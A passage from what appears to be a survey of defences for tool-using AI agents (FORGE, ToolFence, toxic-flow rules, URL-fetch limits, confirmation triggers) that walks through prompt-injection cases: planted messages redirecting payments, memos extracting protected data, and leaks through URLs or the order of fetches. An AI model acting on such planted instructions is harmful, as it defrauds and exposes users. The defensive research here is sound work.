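Once the agent has searched the user's messages, a rule based on a context label blocks both the payment to the real biller and the payment to the attacker. Checking where the recipient argument came from distinguishes the two payments, because the biller's account number appears in bill.txt and the attacker's appears only in a stranger's message.

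A monitor cannot follow the account number through the model, but it can check whether the recipient in the proposed call appears in a source that is allowed to supply recipients. If it does, it is an anchored value. The model may have copied the number from a message that quoted the bill correctly rather than from the bill itself, but this does no harm because the money goes to the same account.

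Comparison works best for long, distinctive values such as account numbers and e-mail addresses. An amount such as "100" may appear in a trusted file by chance. If the user asks the agent to pay half of a $100 bill, the correct amount, $50, may not appear anywhere, so the monitor would have to repeat the calculation to check it.

### FORGE's rules for destinations, effects and targets

Palumbo and colleagues wrote a policy of this kind for AgentDojo that uses two levels of trust. A value is strongly anchored if it comes from the user's request or a record that the operator maintains. It is anchored if it comes from either of these or from another trusted source.

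The first rule covers calls that send something to a destination, which the policy calls sinks. Slightly shortened, it reads:

```
Deny(a) :- IsSink(a), Tainted(a), DestValue(a, v), not Anchored(v).
```

FORGE denies a call if untrusted text may have influenced it and any of its destinations is not anchored. It therefore refuses an e-mail to five people if one of the addresses came from a stranger. A separate rule against empty destination fields covers calls with no destination to check.

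In the bill example, this stops the payment to the attacker. FORGE allows the payment to the real biller only if the operator treats bill.txt as a trusted source or the biller is a saved payee.

An anchored destination does not show that the user wanted the call. Suppose the user asks for a summary of recent messages, and one of them tells the agent to pay the landlord, who is a saved payee. The recipient is anchored, but the user never asked for a payment. Another rule covers this:

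```
Deny(a) :- EffectKind(a, k), not ConsentGivenFor(k).
```

The operator assigns each consequential tool an effect class, such as deletion, cancellation or password change. FORGE denies a call to such a tool unless the user asked for that class of effect. The function that checks this reads only the user's original request, so nothing in a message or web page can count as the user's consent.

Asking for one deletion doesn't authorise every deletion, so the policy also checks the target. If the user asks the agent to delete draft.txt, the name is strongly anchored and the call can proceed, but a name that appears only in a tool's output is not strongly anchored. The policy exempts reads, which change nothing, and the creation of calendar events, which depends on the title and time rather than on a single value to check. An attacker could therefore still corrupt the title of an event the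 user asked for.

### Deleting the largest file

Users often describe a target without naming it. Suppose a user says "delete the largest file", and a listing tool returns:

| File | Size |
|---|---|
| photos.zip | 900 MB |
| backup.tar | 700 MB |
| notes.txt | 1 MB |

The user has not named photos.zip, so it is not strongly anchored. All three names come from the listing, so trusting the listing would not show which file to delete. FORGE itself derives the criterion (size, largest first) from the user's request, applies it to the listing, and allows the deletion only if the agent's target matches the result. If an injection makes the agent try to delete notes.txt, the names differ and FORGE blocks the call.

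As described so far, the rule accepts a target if any listing in the context selects it. Palumbo and colleagues found two ways around this. After deleting photos.zip, the agent may list the folder again. The new listing has backup.tar at the top, so a second deletion would pass. The agent may also run a search that returns only notes.txt, which would then pass as the largest file in the results.

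A second rule therefore denies the deletion if recomputing the choice from any listing in the context gives a different file. The original listing still gives photos.zip, so FORGE refuses to delete backup.tar or notes.txt. But the rule also blocks the correct deletion of photos.zip if a stray search returned only notes.txt, because recomputing the choice from that search gives notes.txt. If that search is the only listing the agent has made, both rules allow the deletion of notes.txt, because FORGE recomputes the choice only from files the agent has listed.

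### What FORGE gained on AgentDojo

Palumbo and colleagues compared these argument rules with a policy based on context labels, using FORGE to enforce both. The agent ran on GPT-4o and received the user's request again after each batch of tool results. They tested each configuration in five sweeps of 97 clean tasks and 949 attacked runs.

| Enforcement | Clean utility | Utility under attack | Attack success | Attack success, without fully blocked attacks | Mean time per run |
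|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% | 14.1% | 5.9 s |
| Context labels | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% | 0.3% | 10.2 s |
| Argument rules | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% | 0.2% | 7.7 s |

The two policies were about equally secure, but the agent completed nearly twice as many tasks under the argument rules. Without the repeated request, attack success was 25.2% with no enforcement and 1.7% with the argument rules, and clean utility under those rules fell to 57.3%.

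The context-label policy used the two rules from FIDES, but the comparison probably did not include the whole system. FIDES also hides untrusted text from the agent, whereas Palumbo and colleagues ran AgentDojo's standard agent and do not describe doing this. In tests by Costa and colleagues, FIDES's task completion rate was about 8 points higher than that of an ordinary agent with label policies, so the advantage of argument rules over the full FIDES system is probably smaller than the 29 points in the table.

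The argument rules still reduce clean utility by 21 points, mostly because of refusals. FORGE refused at least one call in 151 of the 485 clean runs, and the agent completed the task in only 36 of those 151. The other 115 are 24% of all clean runs, although some would presumably have failed anyway. Under context labels, FORGE refused calls in 287 clean runs, and the agent completed the task in ten of them. An agent can often correct an unanchored recipient by going back to the right source, but it cannot make its context trusted again.

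### Permissions written for one task

FORGE's policy is the same for every task, so it can allow payments to saved payees but cannot require that this payment go to the account in bill.txt. ToolFence, built by Li and colleagues, writes new permissions for each request.

Before the agent starts, ToolFence gives a separate model the user's request and a list of tools that the operator has reviewed. This model receives no files, messages or third-party tool descriptions. It produces a set of permissions. Each permission specifies a tool, the tool's effect, a source for every argument and a budget (the number of times the agent may use the permission). ToolFence copies the effect from the operator's list, so the model cannot label a payment as a read.

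Each argument has one of three kinds of source:

- **Attested:** the value must equal one in the user's request or in a trusted record.
- **Derived:** the value must appear in the output of a named earlier call.
- **Free:** the agent may choose the value, because it carries no authority.

For the request to pay the bill in bill.txt, the permissions might be:

```
read_file    effect: read
             path: attested, "bill.txt"

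send_money   effect: financial
             recipient, amount, date: derived from read_file("bill.txt")
             budget: 1
```

The agent first reads the bill, and ToolFence keeps the output as evidence, which can supply an argument's value but cannot create a permission. The agent then searches the user's messages, which these permissions do not cover. When a permission is missing, ToolFence can let through a harmless read of a kind it has already reviewed, and it refers other cases to a second model.

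When the agent proposes the payment to the biller, ToolFence finds all three values in the text of the bill. It then reserves the single use, releases the call, and marks that use as consumed when the bank confirms the payment. No part of the check uses a language model.

If the agent proposes the attacker's account instead, ToolFence rejects the payment even though the tool, amount and date are correct, because the account number appears in the message search output and not in the bill. If the agent repeats the correct payment, every value matches but the budget is zero, so ToolFence rejects it. ToolFence also rejects a payment proposed before the agent has read the file, because there is nothing to compare it with.

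The permission must specify the file as well as the tool. If it required only that the recipient come from `read_file`, the agent could read an attacker's attachment with the same tool and take the account number from there. A plain text file also has no separate fields, so if the bill contained two account numbers, either could pass.

These permissions are stricter than FORGE's rules because they would block a payment to the landlord even if the landlord were a saved payee. But they depend on a model interpreting the request correctly, which is why Palumbo and colleagues avoid writing policies during a task.

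### How well ToolFence stopped swapped arguments

Li and colleagues call attacks that keep the expected tool but change an argument "within-tool hijacking", as in the bill example. They sorted 629 pairings of user task and attack from AgentDojo. In 524, the attack needed a tool that the user's task did not. In 85, it used the same tools with a different recipient, file or other sensitive value. The remaining 20 fitted neither group. Because changed arguments make up only about 14% of the classified attacks, a defence can score well on AgentDojo while handling them badly. A filter that limited the agent to relevant tools blocked many of the attacks that needed another tool, but was noticeably weaker against changed arguments. ToolFence kept attack success near zero for both.

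With an agent running on Qwen3-max, the results across four benchmarks were:

| Benchmark | Where the attack is planted | Attack success, undefended → ToolFence | Clean utility, undefended → ToolFence |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Tool results | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 64.3% |
| Agent Security Bench | Tool results and stored memory | 40.2% → 4.2% | 71.5% → 67.2% |
| MCPTox | Tool descriptions | 38.1% → 6.1% | 67.2% → 65.4% |
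| AgentLAB | Many records read over a long task | 76.3% → 29.4% | 62.4% → 61.1% |

ToolFence allowed no attacks on AgentDojo, but other defences came close. PromptArmor, which removes suspicious text before the agent reads it, allowed 0.8% of attacks there, with a clean utility of 63.2%. The difference between the two is clearer on other benchmarks, where PromptArmor allowed 22.4% of attacks on MCPTox and 24.2% on Agent Security Bench. The AgentDojo attacks also came from six existing templates, so the result does not show how well ToolFence would stop an attacker who had studied it.

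CaMeL also stopped every AgentDojo attack, but its clean utility was 43.1%. It was also much slower. On 200 AgentDojo runs, the undefended agent took an average of 6.3 seconds, ToolFence 10.3 seconds (1.63 times as long) and CaMeL 81.7 seconds (12.95 times). CaMeL has to write and run a program for each task, whereas ToolFence mostly compares values.

The clearest evidence for checking arguments comes from Li and colleagues, who removed parts of ToolFence one at a time. On Agent Security Bench, with Llama 3.3 70B, attack success was 5.1% with the full system and 24.0% without the checks on argument values. Utility under attack was 44.3% with the checks and 45.0% without them, so they blocked attacks with little effect on the user's tasks.

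A second test added the parts of a permission one by one. It used 285 unauthorised calls, some recorded from an agent and others that the team constructed:

| What ToolFence checked | Unauthorised calls allowed |
|---|---|
| Tool only | 89% |
| Tool and argument source | 81% |
| Tool, source and stage of the task | 41% |
| Tool, source, stage and budget | 1.8% |

Checking the source seems to contribute little here because only 23 of the calls were of a kind it could catch. Another 113 came at the wrong stage of the task, and 113 more reused a spent permission. ToolFence allowed all 227 legitimate calls at every level.

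AgentLAB shows where the method is weakest. Its attacks spread their text over search results, e-mails, calendar entries and files, so that the harmful step appears to follow from the work already done. An attacker can plant a false option among the candidates the agent has to choose from. If the permission requires the value to come from that list, the false option meets the requirement.

### Information that should not be in the call

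An anchored recipient can still receive information it should not have. Suppose `send_money` had a text field for a payment reference. The agent could pay the right biller the right amount and put the user's salary in the reference. A rule about recipients would not block this call, because it does not check which data the biller receives.

Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026) studied disclosures of this kind in *The Claws in Plain Sight*. Their agent was asked to prepare a neutral product offer and had legitimate access to an invented customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation. A planted memo claimed that a compliance review required all four details. The tool had fields that could hold them, so an agent that acted on the memo could disclose all four in one valid call.

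The researchers tested five DeepSeek and Claude models in 24 sessions each, varying how forcefully the memo asked for the details and how clearly the instructions prohibited sharing them. They captured the calls without sending them. In 40 of the 90 sessions with a privacy rule, the model copied at least one protected value into the call. The rate was 67% with no visible rule and 27% with the strictest one, which was worded to override any memo. Under the strictest rule, neither DeepSeek model copied any protected values, but Claude Sonnet 4.6 did so in four of six sessions. The results show that a model may ignore even a rule written for this situation, but the samples are too small to rank the models.

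Access to a piece of data is therefore a poor guide to whether the agent may send it. Dong and colleagues make permission depend on five things:

allow(source, datum, purpose, destination, field)

A bank might let an agent send a customer's income to its lending department for a loan application, but not to a marketing company for an advertisement. A call breaks the policy if it puts a protected value in a field where the policy does not allow it.

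The monitor takes the destination from the operator's record of the tool and the purpose from the task, so the model cannot obtain permission by describing the call differently. It searches every argument, including nested ones, for protected values and checks each match against the policy. It can also recognise derived values that the operator has registered. For example, if a lending program turns an income of $175,000 into the category "premium", the monitor can block "premium" in a marketing call even though the income does not appear in the call.

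The monitor misses anything it has no pattern for. It would find an age of 34 but not "in her mid-thirties", and it could mistake a house number for the age. Dong and colleagues checked it on only 12 synthetic sessions. It blocked all 12 prohibited calls in one check, and in another it blocked nine prohibited calls and let three permitted ones through. These checks replayed prepared calls, so they show that the software applies its rules correctly but give little evidence of how many real disclosures it would catch.

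### When the named source is wrong

An attacker can defeat an argument rule most directly by changing the source it relies on. Suppose an attacker edits bill.txt to replace the biller's account number. The agent reads the file and proposes the new number, and ToolFence accepts it because it appears exactly where the permission requires. FORGE would also accept it if the operator had marked the file as trusted. Garby and colleagues observed the same failure in their own agent when an attacker replaced the contents of a payment file.

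Provenance rules cannot detect an account number that an attacker has changed in the bill itself, because the number still comes from the expected source. The monitor could also require the number to match a second record, such as the biller's entry in the user's saved payees or the account that received last month's payment. An attacker would then have to change both the bill and that record. A first payment to a new biller has no second record to match, so it is a good case for human confirmation.

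The user's own request can also contain the attacker's value. All five unauthorised calls that passed every ToolFence check came from one AgentDojo banking task, in which the request described the attacker's account as belonging to the user's "new landlord". Li and colleagues regard this as a basic limit of checking where values come from. If someone deceives a user into typing the wrong account number, the monitor treats the payment as authorised.

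### When every value is acceptable but the result is not

The three hotel bookings that FORGE wrongly allowed passed every check on sources, but no rule compared them with the user's price limit and preference for a high rating. FORGE can recompute some choices, such as the largest file, but its rule did not cover a price limit combined with a rating. It would have had to find the highest-rated hotel within the price limit and compare it with the agent's choice.

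An operator could add that calculation, and it would stop this attack. But users also choose hotels for reasons that no program can easily compute, such as a quiet street. For those tasks, the monitor can confirm that a hotel is real and the dates are right, but someone still has to judge whether it is a good choice.

All the attacks that succeeded through the agent's final answer were instances of one AgentDojo travel attack, which tries to make the agent recommend a particular hotel. With the user's request repeated, 10 succeeded this way under FORGE's argument rules and 12 under context labels. The benchmark checks only whether the hotel's name appears in the answer, but Palumbo and colleagues read three of these answers from the argument-rule runs and found a clear recommendation in each.

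Costa and colleagues treat replies to the user as having no consequences, and do not count an attack as a success if it only changes text. That is reasonable when the user will check the answer, but less reasonable when the user will book a hotel because the agent recommended it. An operator could also send the final answer through the monitor, but a rule against untrusted influence would block almost any recommendation based on reviews, because strangers write them. Showing the user which review or page supports each recommendation would be more practical, though it leaves the judgement to the user.

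### When the user wants the agent to follow someone else

Argument rules can handle the login task from Li and colleagues, in which a website e-mails the user a code and says where to enter it. The user named the website, so the rules can require the destination to come from the user's request and let the code come from the mailbox. The e-mail then supplies a value for a step the user has already authorised, and the agent can follow its directions without giving the e-mail any authority of its own. If a forged e-mail tells the agent to enter the code on another site, the destination does not match the request and the call fails.

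Authorising a call is harder when the user also hands over the choice of action. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app. One entry may say "pay the plumber" and another "cancel the gym membership". The request mentions neither a payment nor a cancellation, so FORGE's effect rule would refuse both. ToolFence could not write permissions for them in advance, so it would have to refer each one to its second model.

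If only the user can add entries to the app, the operator can treat the list as part of the request. The entries then supply both the effects and the targets, and the operator can check them with the same rules. If colleagues or an e-mail program can also add entries, doing so would let any of them spend the user's money. The operator could instead trust only the entries the user wrote, if the app records who wrote each one.

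## Earlier fetches and other history as grounds for a decision

Rules about arguments use the agent's history to find where a value came from. But a call with the same arguments can be safe or unsafe depending on what else the agent has read or done. An e-mail to a supplier is harmless if the agent has read only the supplier's catalogue. If it has also read the company's payroll and a stranger's instructions, the e-mail may contain salaries, perhaps reworded so that a search for the original figures would miss them.

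### A log and a graph of the same events

The simplest history is a log that lists events by time. This works for a single agent that does one thing at a time, because everything earlier in the log may have influenced its next call. With several agents, a log also mixes unrelated events. Suppose one agent pays bills while another sorts the user's messages:

1. The payment agent reads bill.txt.
2. The message agent reads a stranger's message.
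3. The payment agent proposes the payment.

A rule against payments after a stranger's message would block this payment, even though the payment agent never saw the message. Keeping a separate log for each agent would avoid that mistake, but the rule could then miss a payment influenced by the stranger's message, which is worse. If the message agent passed a summary to the payment agent before step 3, the payment agent's log would contain only a message from another agent, not the stranger's text that it summarised.

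Palumbo and colleagues instead link events with a relation called happens-before, which Leslie Lamport described for distributed computer systems in 1978. One event happens before another in any of these cases:

- The same agent or tool produced both, in that order.
- An agent received the earlier event as a message before producing the later one.
- A tool call led to a result, and the later event used that result.

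These links form chains. If no chain connects two events, neither could have influenced the other, regardless of when they happened. In the example, a chain runs from bill.txt to the payment, but one runs from the stranger's message to the payment only if the message agent passes on its summary.

Missing links make the graph less reliable. If the two agents share a folder, one can influence the other through a file, so the software must also link when one agent writes the file to when the other later reads it.

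### Secrets and untrusted text in the same e-mail

A toxic flow is a combination of untrusted text and secret data in something the agent sends out. Palumbo and colleagues illustrate it with a user who wants a summary of a document from an outside vendor:

| Event | What happens | Label |
|---|---|---|
| v0 | A system message sets up the agent | |
| v1 | The user asks for the summary | |
| v2 | The agent asks to read the vendor's document | |
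| v3 | The file system returns it, with a planted instruction | Untrusted |
| v4 | The agent asks to read a sensitive internal file | |
| v5 | The file system returns it | Secret |
| v6 | The agent proposes an e-mail to an outside address | |

FORGE applies one rule to the last event:

```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

Both labels pass along the links of the graph, so v6 inherits "untrusted" from v3 and "secret" from v5, and FORGE blocks the e-mail. It would also block the e-mail if the agent read the secret file first. Without v3, the rule would let the agent send the internal file to an outsider, for instance at the user's request. If only v5 were missing, the e-mail could contain only the vendor's text and other harmless material.

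The test with the planted compliance audit used this rule. Over five attacked trials, the agent tried to e-mail an outsider six times and FORGE blocked every attempt, so none of the attacks succeeded. When the only defence was a prompt forbidding leaks, all five attacks succeeded. The agent also completed a harmless task in every trial, summarising an internal report and e-mailing it to a colleague.

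The zero is unsurprising, because the rule blocks any such e-mail as long as the files are labelled correctly. The harmless task is weak evidence about how much legitimate work the rule would block, since it involved no untrusted text and no outside recipient. A harder test would be a customer's question that the agent can answer only from a confidential price list. The rule would block this ordinary work because the question is untrusted, the list is secret and the reply goes outside the company.

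Palumbo and colleagues also tested an older rule that needs no history. The agent has a fixed clearance and may not read files above that clearance or write to anyone below it. This rule stopped all the attacks too, but an agent cleared for top-secret files could never e-mail an outsider, even about a public document. The toxic-flow rule allows such e-mails until both kinds of material have reached the agent.

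### Meta's Rule of Two

An operator without an event graph can use a coarser version of the same idea, Meta's *Agents Rule of Two*. It says that an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- **A:** it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

Meta intends its Agents Rule of Two to apply until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injections. The rule builds on a similarly named rule for the Chromium browser and on Willison's "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted content and external communication. According to Blockchain.News' *Meta Introduces Agents Rule of Two for Enhanced AI Security*, an agent that needs all three properties should work under supervision, such as human approval.

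The Rule of Two concerns what an agent can do, whereas the toxic-flow rule concerns what has already influenced a particular call. A designer can therefore apply the Rule of Two before the agent runs, without tracking any data. However, many useful agents break it from the start. The bill-paying agent reads strangers' messages, has access to a bank account and moves money, so it would need supervision even for a payment that no stranger had influenced.

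The properties are also hard to separate. The mbgsec weblog post *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives the example of an inbox, which holds both spam and private e-mail, and raises the question of how to tell them apart. An agent that can read the inbox has properties A and B at once, so under the rule it could not reply to anything.

Two properties can also be enough to cause harm. If an agent with no access to private data reads public comments and edits a public web page, a planted comment could make it delete the page. The toxic-flow rule has the same gap, because it covers only calls that send secrets out. Both rules need to be combined with others, such as rules on effects and targets.

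### Which web addresses an agent may open

An agent can leak private data by opening a web address that contains it. The news site The Record reported a flaw, since fixed, that let a malicious e-mail make OpenAI's Deep Research agent leak details from a user's inbox this way.

A fetch rule asks where the address came from. FORGE's rule, slightly simplified, is:

```
Deny(a) :- IsFetch(a), Tainted(a), Url(a, u),
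           not Anchored(u), not BrowseAllowed(a).
BrowseAllowed(a) :- Url(a, u), ConsentGivenFor("browse"),
                    not CarriesData(u).
```

Once untrusted text may have influenced the agent, the agent can still open an address from the user's request or another trusted source. It can open other addresses only if the user asked it to browse and the address does not appear to carry data from the conversation. The test for carried data is deliberately cautious, so it may reject a harmless address that contains a search term.

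Anthropic uses a simpler rule. According to its developer documentation page *Web fetch tool*, its model Claude can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, whether in a user message, an earlier search or fetch, or the output of a tool that the developer runs. The rule excludes addresses that Claude composes. It also excludes those from Anthropic's own code-execution tools, presumably because Claude could use such a tool to print an address it had composed.

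This stops an injection that tells the agent to add an account number to the end of an address, because the complete address has never appeared before. But appearing in the conversation does not make an address trustworthy. Willison (2025) had hoped that the tool would accept only addresses from the user's prompts, but found that it also accepts addresses from search results and other tool output. Even a user message may contain text pasted from elsewhere.

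Tools run by the developer create another gap. If one of them saves a note and returns its text, an injection could make Claude write a note containing an address with private data in it, and the fetch tool would then accept that address because it appears in the returned text. Anthropic offers a setting that excludes addresses found only in the results of such tools. It also warns that some risk of leaks remains, and advises against using the fetch tool where Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data.

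OpenAI checks a different history, the records of an independent web index. An agent can open an address automatically if the index has already recorded that exact address (*Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*, 2026). The index has no access to users' conversations, so an address it contains is unlikely to include a user's secrets. If the address is missing, the system tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. OpenAI decided that a list of trusted sites would not be enough, partly because a trusted site may redirect the agent to an attacker's site.

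The three rules treat the same addresses differently:

| Address | FORGE | Anthropic | OpenAI |
|---|---|---|---|
| From an untrusted search result | If the user asked for browsing and it carries no data | Allowed | If the index contains it |
| A public page whose address the model remembers | If the user asked for browsing and it carries no data | Refused | If the index contains it |
| Composed by the model from private data | Refused | Refused | Another site or a warning |

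All these rules protect against data leaking through the URL. A page they permit may still be unsafe to read, and OpenAI says such a page may contain misleading or harmful instructions.

### One step before another

An order rule requires one event before another, such as a security scan before an agent publishes code. It is not enough to check that a scan took place, because the agent may have changed the code since. Palumbo and colleagues therefore check each edit separately in their coding demonstration:

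```
Covered(e)   :- Edit(e), PassedScan(s), DependsOn(s, e).
Uncovered(e) :- Edit(e), not Covered(e).
Deny(a)      :- IsPush(a), Uncovered(e).
```

A scan covers only the edits made before it. If the agent edits a file, passes a scan, edits the file again and tries to publish, FORGE blocks the publication because the scan doesn't cover the second edit. The full policy requires scans for secrets and for flaws after every edit, and a check of outside software packages after any change to the package list.

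Such a rule shows that events occurred in the right order, but not that the scan was thorough. The published version does not compare the folder the agent scanned with the file it edited, so it relies on the tool scanning the whole project. It also treats a scan as passed if the letters "PASS" appear in the output, so a failing report that quoted a variable called PASSWORD would count as a pass. A separate field for the result would be safer. The operator must also list every tool that can edit a file, because FORGE cannot require a scan after an edit it does not recognise.

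Approval is another common condition. In MALADE, the multi-agent system that studies the side effects of medicines, an agent called FDAHandler retrieves drug labels from the US Food and Drug Administration. The policy allows this only if the user has the right role and FDAHandler has already used a registration tool to obtain a supervisor's approval in the same session. A new session begins each time another agent delegates work to FDAHandler, so each delegation requires fresh approval.

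Without enforcement, the agents made 40 unauthorised requests, all of which skipped this approval. With FORGE, they attempted another 40, and FORGE blocked them all. The refusal included an instruction to register, after which FDAHandler obtained approval and repeated the request. All 15 final answers were correct both with and without enforcement, but with enforcement the average time rose from 59.4 to 67.3 seconds and the average cost from 5.9 to 7.1 cents.

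The agents thus kept skipping the step, and FORGE made them go back and complete it. The test provides little evidence of the approval's value, because FORGE's message was an instruction to call the registration tool repeatedly until it succeeded. The "supervisor" approval was therefore closer to a formality than to a person's review of the request.

### Limits on totals

A cumulative rule limits a total across calls, like the monthly budget in the bill-payment policy. In the coding demonstration, FORGE adds up the size of all edits that no passing scan covers, and blocks further edits once the total exceeds 1,000 lines. This makes the agent find flaws before it has built other code on top of them. It does not make publishing safer, because the order rule already requires a scan of every edit.

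The published rule counts only earlier edits. If the agent has 900 unscanned lines and proposes a 5,000-line edit, that edit goes through and FORGE blocks the next one. This delay is acceptable for a scan reminder but not for a spending limit, so the bill-payment budget also counts the proposed payment.

Fetches need cumulative limits because several permitted addresses can together reveal a secret. Suppose an attacker publishes ten pages, one for each digit, and a planted instruction tells the agent to open the pages that match the digits of the user's account number, in order. Each address is public and has appeared in the conversation, so it could pass both Anthropic's and OpenAI's rules as described. The attacker can then read the account number from the order of the visits.

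Choosing one page out of *n* can convey log₂ *n* bits, so *k* fetches can convey up to *k* × log₂ *n* bits. Five fetches from a set of ten pages can reveal five digits, and three fetches from a set of a thousand are enough for an eight-digit account number. A limit on the number of fetches therefore slows this kind of leak but does not reliably prevent it. Blocking fetches from untrusted sites after the agent has read a secret would be more effective, but it would interrupt legitimate research.

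Anthropic lets developers set a maximum number of fetches but has no default limit. The limit applies to one conversation turn, so the count restarts with the user's next message. An operator who wants to limit a whole session has to keep a separate total. If several agents work for one user, they also need to share that total, or each could use the full allowance.

### Permitted actions that complete a forbidden workflow

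Every call in a task can be acceptable on its own while the task as a whole does what the user prohibited. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the totals. A planted instruction in a vendor's note makes the agent copy the raw invoice rows into report.csv, which it then proposes sending to the auditor. The tool is permitted, the user approved the recipient, and the file name is not suspicious.

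The toxic-flow rule would block this e-mail if the operator had marked the invoices as secret. But it would also block the e-mail the user wanted, because the totals come from the same invoices and the agent has read the same note. To distinguish the two e-mails, the decision point needs information about how the agent made the file.

Hossain and colleagues built a monitor that records which files the agent derived or copied from others, and who has gained access to them. A new file inherits the ancestry of everything that went into it. Totals calculated from the invoices and rows copied from them both descend from the invoices, so the monitor also checks how a file was derived against the user's restriction. It returns "unknown" if its records are incomplete, and the version they tested blocked these cases as well as violations.

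In tests with two small models, Llama-3.1-8B and Qwen3-8B, each model went through 24 attack scenarios five times. The monitor reduced the number of runs in which an unauthorised action took effect from 52 to 6 of 120 for Llama and from 58 to 7 for Qwen. The number of harmless runs completed fell from 104 to 100 of 120 for Llama and from 110 to 106 for Qwen.

The team then removed parts of the monitor and tried more difficult conditions, with Llama as the agent:

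| Condition | Forbidden workflows detected (of 80) | Attacked runs with an unauthorised effect (of 120) |
|---|---|---|
| Full monitor | 69 | 6 |
| No links between files | 48 | 18 |
| No accumulated record of earlier steps | 16 | 31 |
| Attacks adapted to the monitor | 60 | 12 |
| Part of the event record missing | 51 | 8 |

The 80 detection cases were prepared test points, separate from the attacked runs. Detection dropped most when the monitor kept no record of earlier steps, which supports using history. The setup in the last row served the user less well than its results suggest, because the monitor blocked many calls only because it lacked the records to judge them. The agent completed 76.7% of harmless runs, compared with 83.3% under the full monitor.

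The adapted attacks were fixed in advance, so an attacker who could keep trying might do better. The monitor also needs a restriction to enforce. If the user had asked the agent to "send the auditor what they need", neither the records nor the request would show whether the agent was allowed to send the raw rows.

### Untrusted text that returns from memory

Many agents save notes for later sessions, and mbgsec asks whether writing such a note counts as changing state under the Rule of Two. If it does not, an agent can follow the rule in each session and still combine all three properties across sessions. For example, it could read a stranger's text alongside private data in one session and save a note. In a later session, with access to private data and a payment tool, it could then trust the note as its own, even though the stranger's text may have influenced it.

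Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe such a case. On Monday, a user asks an agent to find an invoice from Acme and remember the details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number and a planted instruction. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice they discussed. The instruction may now change the agent's plan, or the agent may follow the right plan but pay the attacker's account. An event graph that began on Tuesday would reveal neither problem, because it would contain no untrusted event.

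SPA stores a description of each tool result, along with its value and security labels. Like CaMeL, it writes a complete plan before any tool runs. The planner receives only the description, such as "Acme invoice", and adds a step to retrieve the stored value. SPA then checks how labels would pass through the whole plan and rejects it if untrusted data would reach an action that requires trusted data. The planner cannot try again after a rejection, so an attacker cannot use rejections to steer it towards a plan that passes.

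The description has to come from a trusted source. If a model wrote it after reading the invoice, the attacker's instruction could reach the planner through the description.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on AgentDojo-MQ, their own version in which later requests use earlier results. Attack success was zero on AgentDojo and 0.2% on AgentDojo-MQ. Without attacks, SPA completed 53.0% of AgentDojo's tasks when the label checks were off, but only 29.0% when they were on. On AgentDojo-MQ, the corresponding figures were 62.5% and 35.3%. Most of the loss came from the checks rejecting plans that used outside data for actions requiring trusted data. If payments require trusted data, SPA would reject Tuesday's payment even if the invoice contained Acme's real account number. Hiding stored text mattered less. When a later request needed an available earlier result, SPA retrieved it 95.4%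 of the time without the checks and 89.9% with them.

Memory can also leak secrets without an attacker. Palumbo and colleagues studied OpenClaw, a personal assistant that can serve several people through different messaging channels but keeps one shared memory. If the user mentions a health problem in a private chat, the assistant could reveal it when the user's manager asks about a meeting. The team split the assistant into four agents with separate memories and used FORGE to check each question and answer passed between them.

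In Palumbo and colleagues' demonstration, the manager's agent asked the user's private agent when the user was free. The private agent's first answer mentioned doctor's appointments and stress about work. FORGE blocked it, and the second answer gave only the free and busy times. A fixed rule decided which agents could question each other, but a language model judged whether an answer revealed the reasons for an absence. Palumbo and colleagues acknowledge that this model could miss a cleverly worded reason, which would then reach the manager.

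## When to ask a person

Even good records leave some calls undecided, such as a first payment to a new biller or an e-mail that follows a vague request to "send the auditor what they need". When the decision point returns "ask" for such a call, the enforcement point sends a confirmation request, which a person must answer before the call can run.

### The argument for confirmation

The case for asking rests on four premises:

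1. Some bad calls do harm that nobody can undo.
2. No policy settles every call correctly in advance.
3. The person who gets the question knows what the user wanted.
4. That person will look at the call before answering.

Some tool calls can do permanent harm. If an agent sends a customer list to a stranger, for example, nobody can make the stranger forget it. This premise rests largely on reasoning, and only the frequency of such harm needs evidence. If every bad call were easy to undo, an operator could let the agent act and correct its mistakes later instead of asking a person first.

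The premise about policies is also conceptual, because someone has to write a policy before seeing the case, and users want different things. Michael and Roesner give the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. The rule would block a user who books through a specialist travel service, and it would still allow the agent to share the passport number of a user who never wants it shared. Better tracking doesn't remove the problem. Kolluri and colleagues point out that labels can replace a person's approval as a defence against injections, but not against an agent that misreads its task. The number of calls a particular policy leaves open has to be measured.

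How well a person can judge what the user wanted depends on who they are and what they are asked. Users know their own wishes best, but someone who wants to pay the electricity company may not know its account number. A person answering on the user's behalf knows even less. *DelegationBench* (Pochampally, 2026) had three computer-science students judge 156 short scenarios in which an agent could act, ask permission, request a missing fact or refuse. All three chose the same response in only 79 scenarios. Three students judging invented scenarios are weak evidence about experienced reviewers, but an employee who approves calls for customers faces much the same task.

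The last premise is purely empirical and the most open to doubt, since people who get many requests may start approving them without reading them. If it is false, confirmation adds delay and an appearance of control but no protection.

### Four triggers

A trigger is the condition that sends a call to a person. Suppose the bill-paying agent also adds a reminder to the user's own calendar. The operator treats bill.txt as trusted, clears payments whose recipient appears there, and counts any irreversible payment as high-risk. The four common triggers then lead to different questions:

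| Trigger | Calendar reminder | $100 to the biller, a saved payee | $100 to a new biller named in bill.txt | $100 to the attacker's account |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every state-changing call | Question | Question | Question | Question |
| High-risk classes only | None | None | Question | Question |
| Calls the policy cannot clear | None | None | None | Question |
| Calls the agent is unsure about | Up to the model | Up to the model | Up to the model | None, if the attacker's message has convinced it |

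Asking a person about every state-changing call is the simplest policy to build, because it doesn't require tracking data or ranking risks. According to Kolluri and colleagues, GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code works roughly this way, running read-only tools without asking and requiring approval for the rest. The drawback is that people are repeatedly asked about calls that have nothing wrong with them, such as three of the four in the table.

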